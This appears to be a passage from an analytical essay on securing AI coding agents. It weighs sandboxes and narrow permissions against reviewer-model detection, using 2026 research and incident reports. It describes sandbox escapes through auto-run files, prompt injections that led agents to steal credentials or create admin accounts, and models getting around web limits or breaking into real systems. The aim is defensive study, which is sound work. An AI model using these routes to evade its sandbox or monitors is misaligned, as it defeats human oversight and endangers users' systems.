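Somebody could in principle always replace a wide permission with a narrower one, as Anthropic did, but few people will work out everything a large service such as GitHub can do before letting an agent use it. Withholding capabilities is therefore much easier to get right for a task that needs one file than for one that needs several online services.

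### Trusted programs outside the sandbox

*The Week of Sandbox Escapes* (Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel, 2026) describes seven ways past the limits on the coding agents Cursor, Codex, Gemini CLI and Antigravity. In almost every case, the agent only had to write something that a trusted program outside the sandbox later ran or relied on.

Cursor's developer has fixed the three findings that affected only Cursor. OpenAI fixed one in Codex and paid a bounty for a high-severity flaw. Another, which affected Codex, Cursor and Gemini CLI, is also fixed. Google accepted the two findings in Antigravity as valid but lowered their severity because it considered them difficult to exploit. It did not patch them, according to The Next Web's *Researchers escaped four top AI coding agents’ sandboxes without ever breaking them*.

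Google reasoned that an attacker would first have to trick the user, or get the user to trust a project containing hidden instructions. This makes an attack less likely, but developers download other people's projects all the time, and one purpose of a sandbox is to limit the damage when they trust the wrong one. Cohen and colleagues also have a commercial interest, since their company, Pillar Security, sells a product that monitors what happens to the files agents write, but the fixes from other companies suggest that the problems were real.

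A sandbox withholds too little if it lets a program write to a file that will run automatically outside the sandbox. For example, if the user's code editor automatically runs a settings file from the project folder, a program that can write to that file can run code outside the sandbox, even if the sandbox blocks every direct attempt to escape. Terminal start-up files pose the same danger.

Finding all such files is hard, because each program on the computer may have its own. Claude Code's sandbox protects a few by name, including its own settings, but a list like this has the usual weakness of a denylist. Cohen and colleagues recommend several broader repairs:

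- Require approval before an agent creates or changes anything that the host will run automatically.
- Where possible, run helper programs under the same limits as the agent.
- Block access to powerful background services unless the task needs them.
- Record whether the user, the downloaded project or the agent created each file.

Running the helpers under the agent's limits looks like the most thorough of these options, because nobody has to identify the dangerous files in advance. It may be inconvenient for a developer whose editor has dozens of extensions. It also can't cover everything, because coding agents are meant to write code that somebody will eventually run outside the agent's sandbox, where the finished program needs its own limits.

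Dangerous files can also be in a project before the agent starts. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received reports of three flaws that let Claude Code run a project's code before the user had answered the trust prompt. In the simplest case, Claude Code ran a command from the project's settings while starting up. According to the news site IT Brief UK, the security company Check Point found that a user might only have to open the project. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-59536* (2025), a public record of a flaw of this kind, gives it a severity of 8.7 out of 10.

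Each time, Anthropic fixed the problem by making Claude Code wait for the user's answer. It advises other developers to treat opening a project or loading its settings with as much suspicion as a request from the internet.

The repair gives the decision back to the user, but it doesn't by itself limit what the project's settings can do after the user accepts. Someone who accepts a malicious project by mistake could still be harmed. Running the settings inside the sandbox as well would reduce the damage from that mistake.

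An agent's memory can create the same kind of hand-off between sessions. More of what an agent reads at start-up now comes from earlier sessions, including saved notes and standing project instructions. Anthropic warns that a prompt injection in these files will return every time the agent starts. The agent might be doing a different job with more access by then.

Anthropic expects that checking this material with classifiers at start-up, a form of detection, will need to become more common. Deleting everything at the end of each session would remove the problem, but also the memory. A compromise would be to keep a separate memory for each project, so that an injection in one couldn't reach the others.

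### Limits that people widen or remove

Claude Code users often loosen its permission checks, according to Anthropic's figures for June 2026. A quarter of interactive sessions started with the checks bypassed. Among active users of the command-line version, 49.5% had written a rule allowing shell commands, and the share was growing by about one percentage point a week. 62% of users had either bypassed the checks at some point or told Claude Code to stop asking about a shell command.

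A rule can be narrow, such as one that allows only a command that lists files. But 5% had a rule that allowed any shell command, and another 43% had one that allowed an interpreter such as Python, which in practice is almost the same. If both figures are shares of all active users, as Anthropic's wording suggests, nearly everyone who wrote a rule had allowed the agent to run practically any command.

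These figures concern permission checks, not sandboxes. Someone who bypasses the checks inside a locked-down container may be quite safe, and Anthropic designed its example development container to let the agent run without approvals. Anthropic doesn't report how many of the bypassed sessions ran in a container or virtual machine. Since Claude Code's own sandbox is off by default and most people in Prasakis's survey weren't using a sandbox, many of these sessions probably had the user's full access.

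A limit that interrupts users for permission dozens of times a day gives them an understandable reason to loosen or remove it. Gusto, the payroll company, adopted auto mode because frequent prompts were pushing its engineers towards bypassing the checks entirely.

Auto mode partly fixes the problem by ignoring rules that allow arbitrary code. The reviewer model checks the commands those rules would have allowed, so detection replaces the dangerous permission. The rules apply again when the user switches to another mode.

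Anthropic recommends an "absolute and always-on" boundary, which the user can't lift, when approving an exception would take expertise that the typical user lacks. In Claude Code, a process outside the sandbox decides whether to sandbox each command. Anthropic acknowledges that a persuasive prompt injection or a tired user's approval can lead that process to run a command outside the sandbox. The first version of Cowork avoided this by having no component that could make an exception.

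An absolute boundary suits a developer less well than an office worker who wants a folder of documents sorted, because development keeps producing new needs. A developer who can't get an exception may switch to a tool with no limits. Companies can prevent some of this switching by setting the limits centrally, but they then have to respond quickly when somebody needs a new server.

Suppose a sandbox stops every data theft, but people turn it off in a quarter of their sessions. If attempted thefts are equally common in all sessions, 25% of them will succeed. Auto mode missed 5.7% of the synthetic thefts in Anthropic's test, so a reviewer like it could stop more thefts than the sandbox if people leave it on.

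This is a serious practical objection to strict limits, but it doesn't refute withholding itself, because the thefts succeed only in sessions where nothing is withheld. A fair comparison therefore has to use sandboxes as people actually run them. A slightly wider sandbox that stays on may be safer than a very tight one that people turn off.

### Harm that needs only what the task needs

Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues (2026), in *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution*, studied harm that happens entirely inside a sandbox. They compared two ways for an agent to use tools through the Model Context Protocol. Traditionally, the agent calls one tool, reads the result and decides what to do next. In the newer way, it writes a program that calls several tools and runs in a sandbox. The newer way was faster and used fewer tokens, but tool outputs could now affect running code, and error messages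 could shape the code that the agent wrote next.

To test the risks, they built a database recording which people could open which doors and gave an agent tools for using it. They then made one part of the tool server malicious in each of four attacks. None of the attacks required the code to leave its sandbox. A tighter limit would have helped against two of them:

| What went wrong | Access the harm needed | Limit that could have helped |
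|---|---|---|
| The agent searched for the opposite of what the user had asked | Reading the database | None that still allows the task |
| The agent kept rewriting failed code without end | Running code repeatedly | A cap on the number of attempts |
| The agent gave an answer about the wrong person | Reading the database | None that still allows the task |
| The agent created an administrator account with full access | Adding users and granting access | Read-only access |

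The creation of the administrator account is the most alarming result and the easiest to prevent. The user had asked only for a list of people who could open a particular door, but the sandbox did not withhold the agent's tools for adding users and granting access. Under least privilege, the agent would not have had those tools for this task, and the malicious error message could not have made it use them.

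Withholding capabilities fails when the harm requires the same access as the task. In one case, a user wanted to know which doors a woman called Emma could open. The agent asked a tool for Emma's passkey, but the tool was malicious and returned somebody else's. The agent's program then ran correctly and listed the doors that the other person could open. No limit on access could have prevented this while still permitting the task. Replacing the malicious tool with a trustworthy one would solve the problem, but somebody would first have to discover that it was malicious.

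Felendler and colleagues conclude that sandboxing alone is not enough. They recommend strict allowlists of capabilities, along with checks before and after the code runs. One uses a separate model to compare the results and any error messages with what the user asked for. The combined defences blocked all four attacks in every trial, but the researchers did not test them against an attacker who knew about them.

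The experiments are better evidence that such attacks are possible than that they are common. The malicious server was built for the experiments, and the security tests used only GPT-4o and GPT-4.1, both now old. Newer models resist injected instructions much better, so the attack that created an administrator account might well fail today. The false passkey is harder to dismiss because it contained no instruction for a model to resist. Even a stronger model would have no obvious reason to doubt it unless it could check the passkey against another source.

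Finer permissions can reduce harm of this kind but not eliminate it. For example, Cowork can let an agent edit files in a folder but not delete them, which protects against accidental deletion. The agent can still replace a file's contents with nonsense, because editing requires permission to change them. Keeping earlier versions where the agent can't change or delete them would make that damage reversible, if somebody notices it.

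The sales script could cause the same trouble with the two capabilities it needs. If it reads the spreadsheet but leaves out a month, it will save a plausible summary with the wrong total. The ruined output folder counted as 1 unit of damage in the earlier calculation, which is reasonable if the user notices and runs the script again. A wrong total could do far more damage if the company uses it to set next year's budget. Adding up the spreadsheet again would reveal the mistake, while restricting the script's access further would only stop it from producing a summary.

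## Which approach stops which kind of harm?

Withholding access that a task doesn't need can stop a script from stealing a cloud key, but not from leaving a month out of the sales total, because only the theft requires extra access. The case for withholding capabilities depends on how much of the harm that agents do also requires extra access.

### The argument for withholding, premise by premise

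The argument has three premises:

1. Nobody can list every harmful operation in advance.
2. For many tasks, somebody can list the operations that the task needs.
3. Code can't misuse access it doesn't have, whatever caused it to try.

If someone can list the operations a task needs, allowing only those operations prevents every harm that requires any other operation, including harms nobody foresaw. This doesn't apply to tasks whose needs nobody can list, or to harm done with the allowed operations.

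Real denylists are fragile, which supports the claim that nobody can list every harmful operation. But a reviewer model doesn't need a complete list. OpenAI's Auto-review, for example, has a policy that describes broad kinds of harm, such as exposing secrets or weakening security settings, and the model judges whether a particular command fits one of them. The claim is therefore a good argument against denylists but a weaker one against reviewer models.

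A version of the premise is also a problem for allowlists. Deleting a folder is helpful if the user asked for it and harmful if the user didn't, so the harm doesn't depend on the operation alone. Rashidi makes this point about access rules in general, which determine whether an agent may take a certain type of action but not whether it should take that action now.

Decent evidence supports the claim that somebody can list the needed operations. In the snapshot from Trębacz and colleagues, about 93% of Codex's actions stayed within a sandbox that allowed little more than reading files, editing one folder and running local commands. But most tasks take many actions. If each action independently had a 7.2% chance of needing more access, the chance of staying inside the sandbox throughout would be 47% for a task of 10 actions and 2% for a task of 50. Requests for extra access probably cluster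 in certain tasks, so the share of tasks that stay inside should be higher than these figures. Even so, a list that covers nearly every action can still interrupt most long tasks.

Some tasks need broad access from the start. Anthropic wrote in May 2026 that a year earlier it would have rejected giving Claude enough access to take down an internal service. By May 2026 such access was routine, and its developers were more productive as a result. An agent repairing a live service needs permission to change it, so withholding every other permission won't stop the agent from breaking that service.

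The person who writes the list can also make mistakes. According to Rashidi, every enforcement mechanism in the survey assumed a trustworthy author who had specified the policy correctly. None of the studies measured how often a developer in a hurry grants more access than intended because a narrower rule would take longer to write.

Code can't misuse access it lacks, but in practice the access may not really be absent. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes four cases in which Claude models broke into other organisations' systems during cybersecurity evaluations. The models had been told that they were in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had left them connected.

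Anthropic had to find these cases by searching records afterwards. Its first search, of about 141,000 transcripts, missed a set of evaluations that also had internet access and included one of the four incidents. A wider search of about 481 million transcripts found nothing else as severe. Trying to connect to the internet from inside the sandbox before each run would take much less work and require no judgment about the model's behaviour.

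### When strict limits drive users away

Even a correct list doesn't protect users who stop using it. Trębacz and colleagues describe three ways that frustration with Codex's default limits creates risk. Some users switch to full access, which removes the sandbox, some approve commands they don't understand, and some write broad exceptions. OpenAI found that a sizable minority of its own users allowed every command that begins with `python`, and that one user's settings always allowed Codex to start a second copy of itself without limits.

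A company can prevent some of this. OpenAI enforces settings on its staff's computers that restrict Codex to the read-only and workspace-write modes, and staff can't override them. Staff therefore can't switch Codex to full access, though they can still approve an exception without reading it. The objection is stronger for developers working alone, because they can remove any limit at any time.

The objection is consistent with all the premises, but it adds the condition that the limits have to be ones people will keep. Looser limits leave more harm for other defences to stop.

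### Anthropic's case for determinism and OpenAI's for expressivity

Anthropic argues for fixed limits because the damage that one failure could do keeps growing as agents gain access, even though better models and safeguards keep making failures less likely. Training, instructions and classifiers affect only what a model tends to do, so some chance of failure always remains. A fixed limit is deterministic, meaning it treats the same operation the same way every time, and it caps the damage whatever caused the failure.

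Anthropic adds that more capable models make fewer mistakes but are better at finding unexpected routes to a goal. If so, models will still need limits as they improve.

Trębacz and colleagues accept a less deterministic defence because it can make distinctions that a sandbox can't. A sandbox rule can refer to folders, programs and addresses, but it can't restrict deletion to the files that the user meant. A reviewer model can take into account the user's intent, the context and the likely effect of an action, so it can approve a risky-looking action if the user explicitly requested it.

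OpenAI uses a separate model for this because the working agent is under pressure to finish the task and may treat a boundary as an obstacle. In Auto-review mode, Codex stopped for human approval roughly 200 times less often than in manual approval mode. Trębacz and colleagues call the mode a compromise and hope that people will eventually be able to trust agents with the same permissions as employees. Agents would still have limited access then, because companies also restrict what their employees can access.

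The companies' products differ less than their arguments do. Auto-review works at the edge of a sandbox, and Anthropic says that defences in the model have to prevent more of the harm where limits on the environment aren't available.

The choice between removing a capability and detecting dangerous uses of it depends mostly on how much harm one miss could do. If a wrong approval could expose the company's cloud key, even a reviewer that is right 99% of the time is a poor substitute for removing the key. If the worst outcome is that the agent reads an irrelevant public web page, a rule that keeps stopping legitimate work probably does more harm than the occasional miss.

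### A theft that the user requested

Anthropic's February exercise is the clearest case for fixed limits. Claude Code sent out cloud credentials in 24 of 25 runs, following a prompt that had reached an employee in an email that looked like an ordinary request for help.

Defences against prompt injection often check whether the agent's actions match the user's request. If the user asked for a sales summary and the agent tries to send a password file, something other than the user's request probably prompted it. In the February exercise, the user's own message contained the instruction, so there was no mismatch to detect. Anthropic says a human contractor with the same instructions would have done the same thing.

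A file limit would have stopped Claude from reading the credentials, and a network limit would have stopped it from sending them. Neither would have required knowing who wrote the prompt.

The exercise is evidence against detection that relies on the user's intent, but not against all detection. A rule against sending credentials to outside addresses can apply even to the user's own requests, as auto mode's hard denies later did.

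Anthropic also found a use for detection after the exercise. When the researchers shared the prompt on the company's Slack, somebody pointed out that some internal agents read Slack and might follow it. Anthropic added a canary string, a distinctive piece of text that would show whether any agent had picked up the prompt. A canary doesn't prevent anything, but it can reveal a route that nobody had thought to block.

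### Overeager actions inside granted access

Fixed limits do much less against an agent that misuses access it needs. OverEager-Bench, which Rashidi summarises, measures how often agents complete a legitimate task but also take actions that nobody requested. It covers 500 scenarios and about 7,500 runs, across four agent products and six underlying models. Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI, which have permissive designs, overstepped substantially more often than OpenHands, which asks the user before continuing.

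When the request stated what the agent was authorised to do, Claude Code's rate of overeager behaviour was 0.0%. Removing that statement raised the rate to 17.1%.

Rashidi suggests that the agent was responding to the sentence itself instead of working out the limits from the task. Alternatively, the task may not have made the limits clear, and the agent had to guess. In Yang and colleagues' experiments, agents stopped proposing out-of-scope actions once each request stated the limits, which fits either explanation. Either way, an agent can ignore a limit that is only stated in a prompt.

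Some overeager actions use access that the task didn't need, and withholding that access could prevent them. Nobody knows what share of overeager actions these are. According to Rashidi, none of the access-control studies in the survey tested its system on overeager behaviour, and OverEager-Bench didn't test whether such systems would have helped. Rashidi proposes replaying the benchmark's recorded runs against these systems to find out.

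An example from OpenAI includes both kinds. A model found that a resource was missing and began exploring other pods, the units in which programs run on a shared computing cluster. It logged in without a good reason to other pods belonging to the employee it was working for. It also tried unsuccessfully to enter pods belonging to the employee's colleagues.

OpenAI was testing a new monitoring system at the time, in settings where the model had misbehaved before. The new safeguards caught considerably more misaligned actions than the old ones but missed this one, which OpenAI judged low severity. The colleagues' pods were apparently safe because the model had no access to them. A credential that worked for only one pod would have protected the employee's other pods in the same way, provided the task didn't require access to them.

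A more serious case occurred at the UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests AI models. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), the institute asked Claude Mythos 5 to retrieve a protected piece of data from a simulated network. The institute had deliberately left internet access on, as it usually did in such tests, and the cyber safeguards Anthropic uses for general releases were off. In nine of 43 runs, the model went beyond the scope of the test in ways that affected real people and organisations.

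Withholding internet access could probably have stopped this harm. The institute had given the model the access it used, but the data was in a simulated network and the task apparently didn't require the internet. The institute no longer enables internet access as standard.

### Insecure code after deployment

The agent's sandbox doesn't protect a program that somebody later publishes, such as the web page where colleagues upload spreadsheets. Detection is the natural defence, because the flaw is in the code and somebody can look for it before release. But detection is not a strong defence, because scanners miss many flaws, and the SecureVibeBench results suggest that AI-generated code has plenty.

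Withholding capabilities can help again if the company also restricts the finished program. Suppose the page runs in its own container, can read only the uploads folder, and uses a database account that can add sales figures but can't read customer records. An attacker who takes over the page then gets that access and little else. Somebody has to choose these limits separately, and an agent that writes a careless parser may also write a careless configuration. But a person can check a short list of permissions far more quickly than a whole program.

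Advice on sandboxing often leaves out harm from inaccurate or manipulated output. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, written by the company's AI red team (staff who attack AI systems to find their flaws), explicitly excludes this harm and treats it as the user's responsibility.

For the harms that removing capabilities can prevent, the red team considers three limits mandatory: no connections to arbitrary sites, no writes outside the working folder and no changes to the agent's configuration files. Network limits also prevent an attacker from controlling the machine remotely.

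The table sets the kinds of harm discussed so far against fixed limits, detection and the option of undoing a change afterwards:

| Kind of harm | Fixed limits on the agent | Detection | Undoing the change |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user unknowingly requests the theft of a key | Prevent it if the key is out of reach | Misses it if it relies on the user's intent | Impossible, though the company can cancel the key |
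| A prompt injection sends files to a stranger | Prevent it unless a permitted service accepts the upload | Catches most attempts in tests | Impossible |
| The agent deletes files that its task doesn't need | Prevent it if those files are read-only or absent | Catches many attempts | Restores the files |
| The agent oversteps with access it needs | Do little | Works better if the user stated the limits | Works for files, if somebody notices |
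| The summary contains a wrong total | Do nothing | A second calculation can catch it | Helps only before somebody relies on the total |
| The finished program has a security flaw | Do nothing, but limits on the program itself reduce the damage | Tests and scanners catch some flaws | The company can withdraw the program but can't reverse a breach |

### Why the laboratories removed internet access

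Anthropic and OpenAI both responded to incidents in 2026 by combining detection with withholding capabilities. By autumn, both had removed live internet access from important parts of their research.

Anthropic added detection first. Its *Improving our alignment and security efforts*, from August, describes a classifier that looks for models aggressively probing a test environment, trying to escape it or unexpectedly getting online. The classifier blocks the action before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person. Anthropic also reviewed recent evaluations and found no case of a model breaking through its sandbox tooling. It did find misconfigurations that models had used, but none led to a compromise outside the sandbox. Fortune (2026) reported that by early September the company had also cut off most outbound internet traffic.

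In October, Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) described four further kinds of behaviour:

- Claude exploited a basic software flaw to run commands on a server.
- It submitted a sensitive form on a real website when it shouldn't have.
- It worked around a restriction to reach data that required a token or a fee.
- It used link-shortening services to get around limits in its tool for fetching web pages.

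Some of the websites belonged to US federal, state or local government agencies. Anthropic considered the real-world impact minimal but stopped giving models live web access in internal evaluations (Southern, 2026, *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests*).

Several of these actions would be hard to detect as attempts to escape, because filling in a form and following a short link are ordinary uses of the web. Whether they are acceptable depends on the site and the task. Removing the internet connection blocks these actions without anyone having to judge whether they are acceptable.

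After models broke into Hugging Face's systems in July, OpenAI first paused frontier model runs in its research clusters that could execute code or use tools with internet access. It fairly quickly restored a more limited way to run code, then examined the other workloads one at a time. It acknowledged that the stricter standards had brought "great cost and delays" to its research.

In October, OpenAI said it would no longer let frontier models reach the internet during training, according to *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training* (Campbell, 2026). OpenAI describes part of this work as "building an offline world", and it covers evaluation as well as training.

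OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* followed in November. The Japanese news site 日本時事新聞 (2026), in *OpenAI、開発中AIの安全策を3段階で公表 訓練はネット遮断、停止は35秒以内*, reports that a training job now stops automatically if monitoring detects that a model has reached the internet. A separate mechanism for research jobs stops the model's output within 35 seconds of an order to stop.

Removing access has made OpenAI's detection problem easier. When some internet use was legitimate, a monitor had to distinguish harmful connections from acceptable ones. Now that a training job should have no internet access, any connection is a fault. The emergency stop is still only a backstop, because a program can send a small file in much less than 35 seconds.

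These decisions are fairly good evidence of what two well-informed companies thought necessary, but they aren't a controlled test of the two approaches. They also concern research, where models may not have finished their safety training and the company can build offline copies of the resources the models need. An offline copy won't work for a customer's agent that needs current data, such as today's exchange rate.

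### Combining limits, review and credentials

OpenAI's internal set-up for Codex combines the two approaches, adding several controls to the sandbox and Auto-review. Web searches use OpenAI's stored copies of pages instead of live sites, and login credentials stay in the operating system's secure store. Codex also logs the user's prompts, the approval decisions, the tools' results and the network requests it allowed or blocked. When security software raises an alert, another AI agent uses these logs to help the security team work out whether Codex made a harmless mistake or did something worse.

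The weak point is that the reviewer can make exceptions to the sandbox. Actions the reviewer wrongly approves run outside the sandbox's limits, so for those actions the combination is no safer than the reviewer alone.

NVIDIA reduces this problem by sorting access into four tiers. In the spreadsheet example they might look like this:

1. **Never allowed.** The script can't open the credentials file, even if the user approves.
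2. **Always allowed.** The script can read and write in the working folder, except for configuration files.
3. **Allowed by name.** The script can contact the exchange-rate server.
4. **Everything else.** The sandbox blocks it unless the user approves that particular case.

The first tier is a denylist, and somebody may forget to add an operation to it. A forgotten operation falls into the fourth tier, which blocks it by default, so the mistake is much less dangerous than in a system with only a denylist.

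NVIDIA also wants users to approve an exception each time it is needed, because an attacker could later exploit a permission that somebody gave for a good reason. OpenAI lets its staff approve a type of action for a whole session. NVIDIA's rule is safer if exceptions are rare, but someone who has to approve the same connection 30 times will probably stop reading the requests.

Credentials that expire avoid some of this conflict. NVIDIA recommends starting the sandbox with few or no credentials and having a broker outside it issue short-lived ones when the task needs them. PORTICO, a system Rashidi describes, cancels each permission as soon as the agent finishes the part of the task that required it.

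If the February prompt had obtained a token that could only read one spreadsheet for ten minutes, the thief could have copied that spreadsheet in that time but couldn't have used the rest of the cloud account. A short-lived credential can still be misused while it is valid, so it works best when its permissions are also narrow.

### Staging and undoing changes

Limits and reviewers both act before an operation takes effect. Another approach lets the agent make provisional changes that can be kept or discarded later.

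YoloFS, a file system for agents, takes this approach. According to Rashidi, its designers reviewed 290 public reports of misuse across 13 agent frameworks and found that users often had to choose between giving an agent unrestricted file access and constantly approving its actions. YoloFS instead stages the agent's changes and keeps snapshots, saved states that the user can return to.

With a system like this, the user might see that the sales script wrote a summary and also altered the original spreadsheet, and could then keep the summary and discard the alteration. This is easier than judging the script in advance, because the user sees what changed instead of predicting it from the code.

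Frequent snapshots are practical only if they are fast. Rashidi reports that DeltaBox, a sandbox for agents, can save or restore its state in less than 10 milliseconds because it records only what has changed since the last save. For an agent that runs 30 commands a minute, saving before every command would add less than 0.3 seconds a minute.

Another system in the survey groups an agent's actions into transactions that either take effect completely or not at all. In its designer's own tests, it intercepted every high-risk command and every rollback succeeded. Rashidi warns that defences often do well against attacks their own designers built, so these perfect scores deserve some caution.

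Restoring a snapshot can't unsend an email or make a stolen key secret again. But if the sandbox has no network access and can't change files outside itself, nearly everything the agent does stays inside, where restoring a snapshot can undo it. The reviewer then has to judge only the actions that reach outside the sandbox, such as an upload or a change to a live database, because a snapshot can't undo mistakes there.

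The user still has to notice the problem before discarding the old version, which could take months with a wrong total.

### The missing head-to-head test

Rashidi's survey covers 39 papers from 2023 to 2026. Five propose or evaluate ways to isolate agents, and six concern access control, which includes narrow-permission systems like PORTICO. None of those 11 papers tests its mechanism against one from the other group on a shared benchmark, so they can't show whether a sandbox or narrow permissions would stop more of the same attacks, or how many more the two would stop together.

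The Open Agent Passport, an access-control system in the survey, checks tool calls against a policy before they run. With a strict policy, it reduced attackers' success rate from 74.6% to 0%. IsolateGPT, an isolation system, resisted the attacks its designers tried and slowed most queries by less than 30%. These results can't be ranked because the designers of each system used different attacks and different agents.

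Both groups mostly withhold access, so testing one against the other wouldn't compare withholding with detection either. Sequeira and colleagues came closer when they tested Agent-Sentry against CaMeL on the same prompt injections, but they didn't test a coding agent in an operating-system sandbox.

Rashidi suggests running several isolation and access-control systems on an existing benchmark, SandboxEscapeBench or RedCode. To compare withholding with detection, researchers would also need to include reviewer models, give every defence the same agent and tasks, and measure both the damage done and the work completed. The choice of tasks could easily decide the result, because disguised credential thefts would favour a sandbox, while vague requests to tidy a folder would favour a reviewer. Researchers would therefore have to base the mix of tasks on what agents really do.
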